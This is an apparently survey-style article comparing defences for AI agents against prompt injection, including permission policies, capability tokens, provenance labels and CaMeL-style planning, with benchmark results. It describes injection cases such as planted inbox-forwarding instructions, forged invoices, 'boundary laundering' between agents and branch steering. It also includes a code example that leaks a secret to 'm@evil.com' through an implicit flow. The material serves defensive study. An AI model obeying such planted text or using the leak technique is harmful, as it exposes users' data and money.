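CapScope has to predict what a task needs before the agent has read anything, but many requests do not contain enough information for that. Shi and colleagues describe a user who asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. Nobody can tell which tools the agent will need until it opens the email.

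Progent starts with a narrow policy and revises it as the task proceeds. A policy is a list of rules, and each rule allows or forbids calls to one tool when the arguments meet certain conditions. A condition can require an exact value, set a numerical limit or match a text pattern. Rules that forbid a call override rules that allow it, and the harness blocks any call that no rule allows.

A language model writes the first policy from the user's request. In the example, this policy allows only a search for Alice's email. The email asks for a summary of the user's recent messages to be posted to the user's Slack account, so the model proposes new rules for reading email, looking up the account and sending Slack messages. When the lookup returns the name `alice`, the model narrows the last rule so that messages can go only to `alice`. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward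 the inbox to an attacker. If the agent tries to do so, the harness blocks the call because no rule allows sending email. The agent receives an error message and can still post the summary.

The model that revises the policy reads untrusted text, so an attacker can deceive it too. Progent therefore checks every revision with a solver, a program that decides whether a logical formula always holds. If the new policy allows no calls that the old one didn't, the harness adopts it automatically. Any other revision needs approval from a person or a fixed rule. Shi and colleagues call this property "monotonic confinement".

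The property prevents permissions from growing unnoticed, but it does not ensure that they are appropriate. Suppose the current policy allows Slack messages to anyone. A deceived model could narrow it to allow messages only to the attacker's account, and the solver would accept the change. The change would permit nothing new, but it would stop the user from sending the message to the right person.

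On AgentDojo, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% with GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer. On Agent Security Bench, another set of simulated agents, it reduced the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Task completion on both benchmarks stayed close to that of the unprotected agent. Most of the attacks that still succeeded on Agent Security Bench used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled legitimate ones. Shi and colleagues excluded two AgentDojo attacks that steer the agent towards a different hotel, because Progent isn't designed to stop an agent from misusing permissions it has been granted.

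In these tests they approved every expansion automatically, to imitate a careless user, so the solver never stopped a revision. The low attack success rates are therefore evidence that the model wrote good rules, not that monotonic confinement works. The first policy, without any revisions, brought the attack success rate on AgentDojo down to 2.5%. Shi and colleagues and, independently, Narisetty and colleagues also tried attacks designed to defeat Progent, but these raised the success rate little or not at all.

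Progent can run inside the agent's code or as a proxy between the agent and its tools. The proxy requires no changes to the agent but can't check the agent's built-in tools. Progent can also apply a separate policy to each sub-agent, as CapScope does, although Shi and colleagues used a single shared policy in their multi-agent test. The task-wide policy in the CapScope experiment resembles that shared policy, but Bouras and colleagues did not test Progent itself.

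### AgentCap: a signed token for each call

*AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) splits the check between two components. A policy engine decides whether to permit a proposed call and, if so, issues a signed token. A gateway in front of the tools verifies the token before forwarding the call. The token names the agent, session, action and resource, and has an expiry time and a maximum number of uses.

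Under their banking policy, the engine lets an agent send money only if it declares that it is paying a bill or sending a payment and already holds a valid token to look up the balance. The agent must also hold no other token that the policy forbids in combination with this one. The token lasts 30 seconds and permits one call. The declared purpose is weak protection because a hijacked model can declare a permitted one.

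The check on the recipient is stronger. The engine records where each value came from and rejects a recipient that appears only in untrusted text. For the invoice assistant, this would block a payment to the attacker's new account number. It would also block a payment to a genuine new supplier whose account number appears only on its invoice, unless the owner had marked that field as trusted.

Each agent also has a trust score between 0 and 1, initially 0.8. Every refused request multiplies the score by 0.7. After two refusals the agent loses the right to make changes, and after three the system isolates it. Sending money requires a score of 0.8, so under the default settings one refusal would suspend payments by lowering the score to 0.56. Each normal action closes 1% of the remaining distance to 1, so the agent would need 79 normal actions before it could send money again. An attacker who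 could provoke a single refusal might stop the firm from paying its bills.

An agent can delegate a token to another agent in the same session. The new token covers the same action and resource, and it cannot last longer or allow more uses than the original. Each delegation reduces how many more times the token can be delegated. The gateway checks the whole chain of signatures back to the policy engine.

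Related designs add other limits. *ToolFence* (2026) reserves one use of a permission before it sends each call, and *DelegateGuard* (2026) ties a delegated permission to a holder and a purpose. PORTICO revokes tokens when a subtask ends, according to *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026).

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao evaluated AgentCap on 949 attacked tasks from AgentDojo and 1,054 from InjecAgent, another benchmark that tests agents against planted instructions. The table compares each model with and without AgentCap. Completion means finishing the user's original task during an attack.

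| Benchmark and model | Attack success, without → with | Tasks completed, without → with |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% → 5.09% | 73.61% → 74.88% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% → 0.00% | 75.68% → 75.04% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% → 8.63% | 74.10% → 62.24% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% → 0.00% | 72.96% → 65.37% |

Without an attack, AgentCap reduced task completion by 3.1 to 11.7 percentage points. Each result comes from a single run, so the random variation is unknown.

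Some of the attacks that succeeded against GPT-4o only required the agent to write a certain reply, which a check on tool calls can't prevent. In the others, the policy did not protect the relevant argument or did not label the source of the attacker's value. GPT-5.4 faced the same attacks under the same design, so its results of zero successful attacks are probably partly due to the model's own resistance and do not show that the policies had no gaps.

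AgentCap also did better than Progent in a direct comparison using GPT-4o on AgentDojo. AgentCap completed 78.35% of tasks without an attack and 74.88% with one, compared with 68.04% and 59.64% for Progent. However, Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote AgentCap's policies in advance, using descriptions of the tools and of the benchmark's user tasks, whereas a model wrote Progent's while each task ran. A company that deploys an agent usually won't have a list of everything its users will ask.

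The checks are fast, with a median time below 0.2 milliseconds for each one measured, but writing the policies is harder. In a customer-service policy, AgentCap's analysis tool detected two conflicting rules that prevented any agent from ever obtaining permission to delete a customer.

### What is lost when the model names resources

Bouras and colleagues state that CapScope is not an object-capability system, because the model still names resources with strings and a table determines whether each call is allowed. Progent works the same way. AgentCap's tokens look closer to classical capabilities, but its software requests a token to fit each call only after the model has proposed it, so the model never chooses which permission to use. A token's signature prevents forgery, but the policy checks have to catch a call made for the wrong person.

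If the invoice assistant may pay only approved suppliers, a permission table blocks payments to a new account as well as capability references would. The two methods differ when an agent holds several permissions for different purposes.

Suppose a patcher can write to `src/fees.py`, which it has to repair, and to a `logs` folder. It reads its log's location from a settings file, where an attacker has changed the location to `src/fees.py`. The patcher then writes its log over the source code. CapScope allows the write because one of the patcher's capabilities covers that path, although the user granted that capability for the repair. Hardy's compiler destroyed the billing file in the same way. If the patcher wrote its log through a reference to the `logs` folder, the attacker's path would have no effect. CapScope could get the same protection by giving the logging job to another sub-agent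 with its own store, but this would require more delegation.

A string, such as a file path, must also refer to the same thing when it is checked and when the tool uses it. CapScope resolves symbolic links before it compares paths, but another program could replace a file with a link between the check and the moment the tool opens the file. Giving the tool a reference to a file that is already open avoids this problem, because the tool doesn't have to look up the name again.

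Rules are also harder to write for resources that the agent discovers during a task. In Progent's Slack example, a model has to read the name `alice` in a tool's output and write it into a rule. In an object-capability design, the lookup tool could return a reference for sending messages to the user's own account. The agent would need no new rule, and a planted instruction could not make the reference point to a different account.

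Permission tables can also enforce only the conditions their policy language can express. Progent's rules apply to one call at a time, so they can cap a single payment but not the total for a month. AgentCap can limit the number of calls, but an agent that delegates a token can't narrow the resource the token covers. A programmer using object capabilities can write a small forwarding object that caps the monthly total or narrows the resource.

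Hardy warned against adding capabilities to traditional mechanisms, because in some systems that combined them, the disadvantages of both outweighed the benefits. His own system, KeyKOS, was built on capabilities throughout, and he reported that such systems were usually smaller than comparable ones that used access lists. Developers of coding agents can't easily follow his advice, because an agent's most useful tool is the shell, which takes commands as text and finds most files by name.

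## The case for tracking where data came from

Permission checks determine which actions an agent may take, but many attacks can succeed using only permitted actions. Suppose the firm with the invoice assistant takes on new suppliers every week. The owner can't list every payee in advance, so the grant has to cover payments to new accounts, perhaps up to €5,000 each. An attacker invents a cleaning company and sends a forged invoice for €3,000. The assistant reads it and copies the account number into a payment call. Progent's rules would allow this call, and so would a correctly implemented payment capability with a €5,000 limit.

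This is misuse within the grant, an attack that reaches its goal using only actions the agent is allowed to take. A narrower grant reduces the damage but doesn't remove the problem. A lower payment limit makes each theft smaller. A list of approved suppliers blocks payments to anyone else, but someone has to add each new supplier, and if that person or program relies on the invoices, a forged invoice can get the attacker onto the list.

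Advocates of provenance tracking conclude that the harness should also check where the details of an action came from. It could then let the owner's request and the firm's own records determine who gets paid, but not a stranger's invoice. AgentCap does a simple version of this check by rejecting a recipient that appears only in untrusted text. More complete designs track data through the whole task, including values that a program or model computes from other data.

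### Labels and the Biba rule

Information-flow control attaches a provenance label to each piece of data and uses the labels to decide where the data may go and what it may influence. The confidentiality part of a label lists who may read the data. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give the rule for combining two sources. If A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another, then only B and C may read a text that draws on both:

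`{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}`

The integrity part of a label records how far to trust the data, and anything computed from untrusted data is also untrusted. *SPA* (2026), a design for agents that persist across several requests, applies this rule to language models. A model's output inherits the labels of everything the model read, so an attacker can't get planted text labeled as trusted by having a model rewrite it.

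The integrity rules date from a model that K. J. Biba published in 1977. As Narisetty and colleagues restate them, a program that reads data below its own level of trust drops to that level, and no program may write to anything above its level. Under these rules, once an agent's model has read untrusted text, it may not authorise an action that requires trust, such as a payment. Only a trusted source can lift the restriction, for example when the owner confirms the account number.

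An ordinary agent keeps its whole conversation in one stream of text, so one untrusted email lowers the label of everything that follows. Specialists call this spread of restrictive labels "label creep", a term also used in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026). Under a strict Biba rule, the invoice assistant could not pay anyone after opening its first message. CaMeL and FIDES both try to enforce the rule while still letting the agent get work done.

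### CaMeL: planning before reading

Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published CaMeL in 2025. It develops a proposal by the programmer Simon Willison to divide an agent between a model that plans and a model that reads. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe its parts. Given the request "pay this week's invoices", CaMeL would work as follows:

1. The planner, a model that sees the owner's request and the tool descriptions but no mail, writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
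2. An interpreter runs the program. It fetches the invoices and stores them as values that the planner never sees.
3. When the program needs a detail from an invoice, the interpreter sends the text to a quarantined model. This model has no tools and can only return values, such as an account number and an amount.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and its permitted readers, and carries the labels, which CaMeL's creators call "capabilities", over to anything the program computes from it.
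5. Before each tool call, a policy written for that tool checks the labels on the arguments and allows or blocks the call.

The program might look like this, where `ask_reader` calls the quarantined model:

```
for invoice in get_invoices("this week"):
    bill = ask_reader("Find the account and amount", invoice)
    pay(bill.account, bill.amount)
```

A planted instruction to forward the mailbox has no effect, because the planner finished the program before any model opened the invoice. The forged invoice is harder to stop. The quarantined model correctly returns its account number, which belongs to the attacker, so only the policy check can catch the fraud. If the policy for `pay` accepts account numbers only from the owner or the firm's supplier records, it blocks the call, because `bill.account` carries the invoice's label. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) gives a similar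 example, in which planted text alters a recipient's address and CaMeL blocks the resulting data flow.

The policy has to accept the amount from the invoice, so a genuine supplier can still overcharge. Like AgentCap's check, the policy also blocks payments to honest new suppliers. In such cases, according to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL asks the user to approve the action. Tracking therefore gives the owner a chance to stop a payment to the attacker that would otherwise go through unnoticed, but the owner may not recognise the forgery.

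According to reported results relayed by Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and no injection within its threat model succeeded. It used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) gives a completion rate of 67%, possibly from an earlier version of the results. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that switching on the policy checks halved CaMeL's completion rate on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Without those checks, CaMeL would pay the forged invoice, so a completion rate measured without them does not show how much preventing misuse within the grant reduces task completion.

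### FIDES: hiding only what would lower the label

CaMeL's planner must plan every step in advance. FIDES, the design by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, keeps the ordinary loop, in which the model receives each result before choosing the next action. When a tool returns data, the harness compares the label on each field with the label on the conversation. If adding a field would make the conversation's label more restrictive, the harness stores the field in a variable and gives the model only a name such as `#read_emails_0.subject`. The model can pass the variable to another tool without reading it, query a quarantined model about its contents, or open it, which tightens the restrictions on later calls.

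Suppose a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, to create a calendar event. The agent needs information from the emails to plan this. It queries the quarantined model about whether there is a request, and the harness restricts the answer to true or false. The agent reads that answer. If the answer is true, the agent has the quarantined model extract the date and guests into a variable, which it passes unread to the calendar tool. An attacker's email can affect the plan by only one bit, and a policy may allow that risk. But the attacker can still choose the date and guests, since they come from the email.

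FIDES combines two basic policies. One allows an action with serious consequences only if trusted data led to it, and the other allows a message only if every recipient may read everything in it. A policy can also treat an action's arguments separately, for example by requiring a trusted recipient but accepting untrusted text in the body.

Costa and colleagues tested the design on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The table shows the share of tasks it completed when there was no attack and, from separate runs, the number of attacks that succeeded.

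| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 152 |
| Ordinary, with policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 0 |
| FIDES, no policies | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% | 21 |
| FIDES, with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 0 |

The attack counts exclude cases that the benchmark scored as successes but that Costa and colleagues inspected and judged harmless or wrongly scored. Label creep explains why the ordinary agent's task completion collapsed in banking and Slack once the policies were on. FIDES recovered part of the loss there but still completed far fewer tasks than an agent with no protection. In travel, FIDES did worse than the ordinary agent, because the policies there allow many tools to run after the agent has read untrusted text and because GPT-4o often failed to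 use the variables properly. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 16% more tasks on average than the ordinary agent under the same policies.

The zeros depend on how the researchers assigned the labels. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, so the labels fitted the attacks in advance. A firm deploying such a system must decide which fields to distrust before it knows what attackers will try. The experiment is good evidence that correct labels and suitable policies stop these attacks, but it does not show that a firm would get the labels right.

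Fan, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security*, focus on the role each argument plays in a tool call. Their system, PACT, would let a web page supply the body of an email but not its recipient. With GPT-4o-mini on AgentDojo, PACT completed 46.4% of tasks and CaMeL 30.9%, and both blocked every attack. Fan and colleagues attribute the difference to the way CaMeL and FIDES judge a call as a whole. That description does not fit FIDES, which Costa and colleagues designed to allow a trusted recipient with an untrusted message. Some comparisons also used simplified reimplementations of CaMeL and FIDES. Stronger evidence for tracking roles comes from a controlled test in which removing them from PACT reduced task completion by 60 percentage points without improving security.

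### Implicit flows and side channels

Labels follow data that a program copies or computes. Information can also escape through the program's choice of what to do next, which is called an implicit flow. Garby and colleagues show how CaMeL's interpreter can miss one. The following is a version of their example in which the bank balance is secret:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: tmp = False
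if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above 10,000, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label, and the program then skips `rich = False`. The interpreter labels only the assignments it runs, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The attacker learns whether the customer is rich, although nothing in the email carries a secret label.

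An attacker who can only plant text in an email would struggle to exploit this flaw, because CaMeL's planner never reads the email and so would not write such a program at the attacker's request. The flaw matters more if the planner is hostile, as in TACIT's threat model, or if an attacker's text reaches the planner by another route.

The code around the interpreter can also leak information. CaMeL runs each program inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt may reveal one bit. Garby and colleagues point out that nothing limits the number of attempts, so an attacker could collect the whole secret one bit at a time.

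A side channel reveals information through a program's behavior, such as its running time or its errors. In Tallam and Miller's example, a program reads a secret number and fetches a web page that many times, so anyone who can see the server's log can learn the number by counting the requests. Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL's creators demonstrated two leaks in their own system, one through an indirect dependency and one through exceptions. Tallam and Miller suggest capping such loops or merging the requests into one, returning errors as ordinary values, and padding sensitive operations so they always take the same time.

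Costa and colleagues deliberately exclude implicit flows from their guarantee. FIDES can stop the agent from copying a secret into a public message, but an observer may still infer something about the secret from which tools the agent calls. They argue that a stricter rule would effectively forbid any publicly visible action once the agent has read a secret.

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents that enforces a stricter rule. They used the proof assistant Lean to prove that it has noninterference, which means that changing a secret does not change the probabilities of what an outsider sees, except through whether the program finishes. A program can raise a value's trust level only through an explicit `endorse` operation, which an auditor can find in the code. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in LLMbda completed about as many tasks as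 CaMeL did without its policy checks, and attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 attacked runs. This suggests that strict tracking can leave an agent useful, at least for one small group of tasks.

### Wrong and missing labels

Every later check relies on the first label, so the software that assigns it belongs to the trusted computing base. Narisetty and colleagues found this labeling step under-specified in every system they surveyed. These systems normally trust whatever the user types. If the owner pastes the forged invoice into the request, CaMeL's planner treats it as the owner's words. In the deployed form of FIDES, data with no label counts as trusted, so if a programmer forgets to label untrusted data, the system trusts it.

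An accurate label can also give false confidence. A mail server can often verify that a message came from a supplier's domain. But if an attacker has broken into the supplier's mailbox, fraudulent bank details sent from it will still be correctly labeled as coming from the supplier.

Automatic labelling is not yet accurate enough to settle whether tracking where data came from can secure agents in practice. Fan and colleagues report that, on 20 real tools, PACT correctly identified the source of a value 77.4% of the time and the role of an argument 87.1% of the time. When unsure, it chooses the more restrictive label, so some errors block tasks instead of letting attacks succeed.

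Labels also disappear when data passes through software that the harness can't inspect, such as another company's service. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) therefore checks each call immediately before it runs. It searches the arguments for known secrets, including encoded copies, but can miss a secret that a model has paraphrased, translated or split into pieces. It also compares the call's effects with permissions compiled from the user's request. Li and colleagues removed parts of the system one at a time across 1,167 paired cases and found that most of the security came from this check on effects, not from tracking the paths that data took.

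That finding counts against relying mainly on provenance. But how much to rely on provenance and how much on permission checks probably depends on the attacks. A permission check handles planted instructions to do something the user never requested, but it would not stop the agent from paying a forged invoice if the user had asked it to pay that invoice. The version of PACE tested also lacked the full guarantee that Li and colleagues prove, because it could restore a call that the path check had blocked.

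### When one agent instructs another

CaMeL's guarantee covers a single agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system with an orchestrator, a database agent and a notification agent, all running CaMeL with GPT-5.2. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. The database contained a planted instruction to also email the applicants' details to an outside address.

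The planners in the orchestrator and the database agent never saw the instruction, so their programs did not change. The orchestrator then inserted the summary into its request to the notification agent:

```
notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")
```

CaMeL treats the request an agent receives as trusted. The notification agent's planner therefore treated the planted instruction as part of the request, and wrote a program that sent the message to Julie and emailed the data to the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering". They prove that if agents can pass tool results to one another, then in any hierarchy of two or more agents with an untrusted source, some user request will let untrusted text shape an agent's plan.

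The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request that one agent sends another into a `message` and `variables`. The receiving planner reads the `message`, which contains only instructions. The `variables` hold the data, which the planner can use by name but can't read. The interpreter rejects any `message` that depends on a tool's output, and the labels stay attached to the variables when they reach the next agent.

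Peters-Gill and colleagues tested this on a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents, with 949 attacked tasks for each model. The table gives the attack success rates.

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
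| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% |

Every attack that succeeded when each agent ran CaMeL used boundary laundering. Only about nine attacks succeeded in 4,745 runs, so the three-agent example and the proof are better evidence of the problem than the benchmark. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran every test without tool policies. The results show that planted text could not add steps to a plan, but they do not apply to the forged invoice, where the plan is correct and the account number is wrong. Multi-CaMeL also inherits the gap in CaMeL's tracking of implicit flows, and untrusted data can still decide which branch of an existing plan the program takes.

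The protection made the agents less useful. On 112 tasks from AssetOpsBench, a benchmark about managing industrial equipment, running CaMeL in each agent lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2 points. For the two strongest models, the losses were 13.4 and 0.85 points. Most failures occurred because the planner had to commit to a plan before seeing any data. In several cases, an agent that could not find records for the requested dates returned records for nearby dates instead, and the program that had called it continued as if the dates were correct.

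### Changes for business use

Tallam and Miller identify three gaps in CaMeL that a company would need to close. It trusts the user's first message, does not inspect the agent's final answer, and needs better labels for files that users upload. They propose scanning the first message for suspicious links and phrases, scanning answers for planted instructions, and labeling every value from an uploaded file. A policy can enforce the labels reliably, but the scans rely on guesswork. If an answer persuades the owner to pay the attacker by hand, no tool policy applies to that payment.

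They also want stricter checks for riskier actions. Read-only actions on public or openly shared data would need only a basic provenance check. Changes within the user's own files would need a quick confirmation if any argument were untrusted. Emails, bank transfers and other actions that are irreversible or visible to outsiders would need the full label check and multi-factor approval. This would protect the firm from the forged invoice, but the owner would have to approve every payment, which removes much of the reason for having the assistant. Read-only actions also need care because they can leak data. An agent that requests a web address containing a secret reveals it to whoever runs the site.

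CaMeL's second, quarantined model adds delay, which Tallam and Miller estimate could exceed ten seconds for a request involving ten emails. They suggest reusing plans for common requests, replacing the quarantined model with ordinary parsers where the data has a fixed format, and combining several extractions into one call. They say reused plans and parsers cut tokens and delay by up to half in internal tests, but they give no details of those tests.

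Maintaining the policies may be harder. In CaMeL, each tool's policy is a separate Python function, so a company with hundreds of tools could end up with hundreds of slightly inconsistent rules. Tallam and Miller recommend a shared policy language, so that a rule such as "share only within the company" is written once. They also recommend replacing CaMeL's Python with a smaller language and proving noninterference for its interpreter. Garby and colleagues have since proved noninterference for LLMbda, but a company would still have to write its own policies and assign its own labels.

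## The case that general-purpose agents cannot be both useful and guaranteed safe

All the designs described so far require somebody to decide in advance what an agent may do or which data may influence it. This is manageable for an assistant that pays invoices. But developers typically aim to build a general assistant, which has a shell, a browser and a mailbox and does whatever its user asks. Sceptics doubt that anyone can write rules that stop attacks on such an agent and still let it do its work.

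In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) think it "unlikely that general-purpose agents can provide meaningful and reliable safety guarantees" as long as agents and their defences rely on current language models. They are not opposed to security by design, and one of them, Edoardo Debenedetti, led the work on CaMeL.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues argue that any guarantee of safety has to come from the software around the model. Developers can train the model to ignore planted instructions or add a detector for them, but these methods make attacks harder without ruling them out. The similar problem of making image classifiers resist deliberately altered pictures is still open after more than a decade of research. They therefore propose that once a model has read untrusted input, it must be impossible for that input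 to trigger any action with harmful side effects. An agent built this way can't do arbitrary tasks, because some tasks consist of acting on what a stranger wrote. Their argument is a judgement about current models, not an impossibility proof, but it leads them to ask which useful agents developers can build within the restriction.

### Six restricted designs

They describe six patterns. CaMeL is an example of code-then-execute.

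| Pattern | How it works | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results. | Requests that nobody put on the list, and tasks that require reading a result |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes its sequence of tool calls before it reads any outside data. | Tasks in which one result determines the next step |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no. A later stage combines the answers. | Tasks that don't divide into separate documents and simple answers |
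| Dual LLM | A planning model handles untrusted text only through variable names, while a model without tools reads it. | The planner's ability to react to what the text says |
| Code-then-execute | The planner writes a whole program, which calls tools and reading models. | Any step that the program did not anticipate |
| Context minimisation | The system turns the user's request into, say, a database query, then deletes the request before a model writes the reply. | Replies that depend on wording the query left out |

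The patterns also differ in how much an attacker can still do. Under plan-then-execute, an assistant that sorts a user's files might commit to using only `find` and `mv`, which search for files and move them. A planted instruction could still make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. Under map-reduce, one model reads each file and answers only whether it concerns, for example, tax. A malicious file can then end up in the wrong folder but can't affect the other files.

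The loss of usefulness is clearest in Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' example of an agent that answers questions from a database. To keep planted text away from the model, the agent writes its query and its analysis code without seeing what the query returns. It can still chart the salaries in one department, but it can't notice that the results don't contain the answer and try a different query, as analysts routinely do.

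### When a stranger's message decides the action

FIDES could create a calendar event from an email because the user had already named the action, and the email supplied only the date and the guests. Some requests leave the action itself open, like the one to carry out Alice's to-do list. In a similar case from *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026), the user asks the agent to follow John's emailed instructions for updating their code repository. CaMeL's planner can't write a program for this request without reading the email, and reading it exposes the planner to whatever the email contains. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) defends separating planning from reading, but calls this a fundamental limitation of the approach.

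Suppose the owner of the small firm tells the assistant to deal with the morning's emails about Thursday's project call. In one, a consultant the client has just hired asks to join the call. In another, an attacker posing as a newly hired consultant makes the same request. To grant either request, the assistant would use the same calendar tool to add an outside address, found only in a stranger's email, to the same meeting.

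A strict policy that accepts only addresses from the owner or the firm's address book keeps the attacker out, but the real consultant never gets an invitation. A looser policy that accepts addresses from incoming mail lets the attacker join the call. Tightening the policy language doesn't help, because any rule based only on the tool, the arguments' types and their provenance labels must treat the two requests alike. Object capabilities have the same problem, because an assistant holding a reference that can invite anyone can invite the attacker, and one holding references only to known contacts can't invite the consultant.

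The firm could check whether the address belongs to the client's domain, or ring the client. The assistant could ask the owner, who may not know. A language model could judge which email sounds genuine, but then the decision again depends on a component that an attacker can deceive. Somebody could write finer rules in advance for familiar kinds of request, but Foerster and colleagues point out that this takes expertise most users lack, and that users differ in what they are willing to share. They expect that a specially trained model would have to write many of the rules, and that some would be wrong.

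Genuine instructions can also look suspicious. In one AgentDyn scenario, a friend emails the user asking her to buy a replacement light bulb and includes a username and password so she can pay from the friend's account. The request is genuine, but a sensible filter would probably reject it.

### CaMeL, Progent and DRIFT on open-ended tasks

Li and colleagues built the AgentDyn benchmark because they thought earlier benchmarks made defences that stick to an initial plan look better than they are. By their count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after reading something. All 60 AgentDyn tasks, which they wrote by hand, require such a change. The tasks cover shopping, GitHub and everyday errands, and each includes at least one genuine instruction in outside content, such as a notice that the bank has emailed a one-time password. The average task takes 7.1 steps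 with 33 tools available, compared with 3.5 steps and 20 tools in AgentDojo.

Combining the tasks with 28 attacker goals gave 560 attacked cases. The planted text appears only where an outsider could plausibly put it. On a web page, for example, it goes in an advertising banner, not in the owner's own text. The main attack surrounds the attacker's instruction with claims that it is important.

DRIFT, the third system in this comparison, makes a plan and constraints at the start, then uses a validator to check whether later departures from the plan are acceptable. Each cell in the table gives the share of tasks completed when there is no attack, followed by the attack success rate.

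| Model | No defence | CaMeL | Progent | DRIFT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 53.3%, 37.8% | 0%, 0% | 6.7%, 1.7% | 30.0%, 0.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 51.7%, 20.6% | 0%, 0% | 25.0%, 1.6% | 36.7%, 1.1% |
| GPT-5.1 | 61.7%, 5.0% | 0%, 0% | 15.0%, 1.2% | 1.7%, 0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 71.7%, 0.9% | 0%, 0% | 16.7%, 0.2% | 28.3%, 0.2% |

CaMeL completed no tasks with any of the 12 models tested, so its perfect security score here means little. Progent can revise its rules during a task, but Li and colleagues found that it struggled to assign the right permissions when there were many tools. Its mistakes accumulated until it blocked nearly every useful action. It also protected some models poorly, perhaps because it relies on a model to write its rules. With Qwen3-235B, attacks succeeded in 13.6% of cases with Progent and 22.7% without it.

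*DRIFT* (2025) reports a similar pattern on the six AgentDojo tasks that its developers identified as open-ended. An undefended agent completed 25.7% of them, DRIFT 17.8% and CaMeL none.

These results are strong evidence that a fixed plan fails on tasks chosen to require replanning. They don't show how much work a firm would lose, since a real workload would mix such tasks with simpler ones. With only 60 tasks, each one moves a score by 1.7 percentage points. Li and colleagues also told the agents to finish without asking the user for confirmation, which a deployed agent could normally do. Three of the researchers helped develop DRIFT, though they report its losses as plainly as the others'.

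Some of CaMeL's failures may also be avoidable. Its programs can contain branches, so the planner could include a step to fetch a one-time password from the mailbox in case the bank asks for one. No branch would help with "follow John's instructions". The overall scores combine both kinds of failure, and better planning could fix only the first. None of the ten defences in the study used object capabilities in the classical sense, so the case against classical object capabilities rests on the argument about the consultant, not on measurement.

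### Agents that work through a screen

Progent and CaMeL check calls such as `send_money`, where the name and arguments show what will happen. A computer-use agent looks at a screen and issues commands such as `click(x, y)`. The same click could log in, delete a file or open a malicious site, depending on what the screen shows at those coordinates, so a policy has almost nothing to check.

Foerster and colleagues nevertheless adapted CaMeL to such agents. A planner without access to the screen writes a complete program with a branch for each situation it can predict. While the program runs, a separate vision model identifies what is on the screen or where to click. Before acting, the program checks whether a predicted situation applies, such as a cookie notice showing, and selects the matching branch. These plans averaged 213 lines of code and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and fewer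 than 4 branches for CaMeL's AgentDojo plans.

They tested the system on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in ordinary programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice. With Claude Sonnet 4.5 operating the screen, the system completed 28.4% of 109 tasks on the first attempt, and 56.9% when a task counted as solved if any of five attempts worked. The abstract describes this as retaining up to 57% of a frontier model's performance, so the 109 tasks are apparently those that Claude had solved without protection. If so, a single attempt preserved less than a third of the unprotected agent's successes. The five-attempt figure also assumes that someone can identify a successful attempt and discard the rest, which is a problem for tasks such as booking a flight, where a failed attempt may leave a wrong booking.

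The paper claims that UI-TARS, a small open model, improved from 24.4% without protection to 29.0% with it. The higher figure counts the best of three attempts.

The fixed program prevents planted text from adding new actions, but an attacker can still influence which branch the program takes. Foerster and colleagues call this "branch steering". In their demonstration, an advertisement imitates a cookie notice. The plan already includes a step for dismissing cookie notices, so the agent clicks on the advertisement and lands on the attacker's site. The researchers tried two checks: comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code, and asking an independent model. Attacks got past both, and broader settings flagged more harmless pages.

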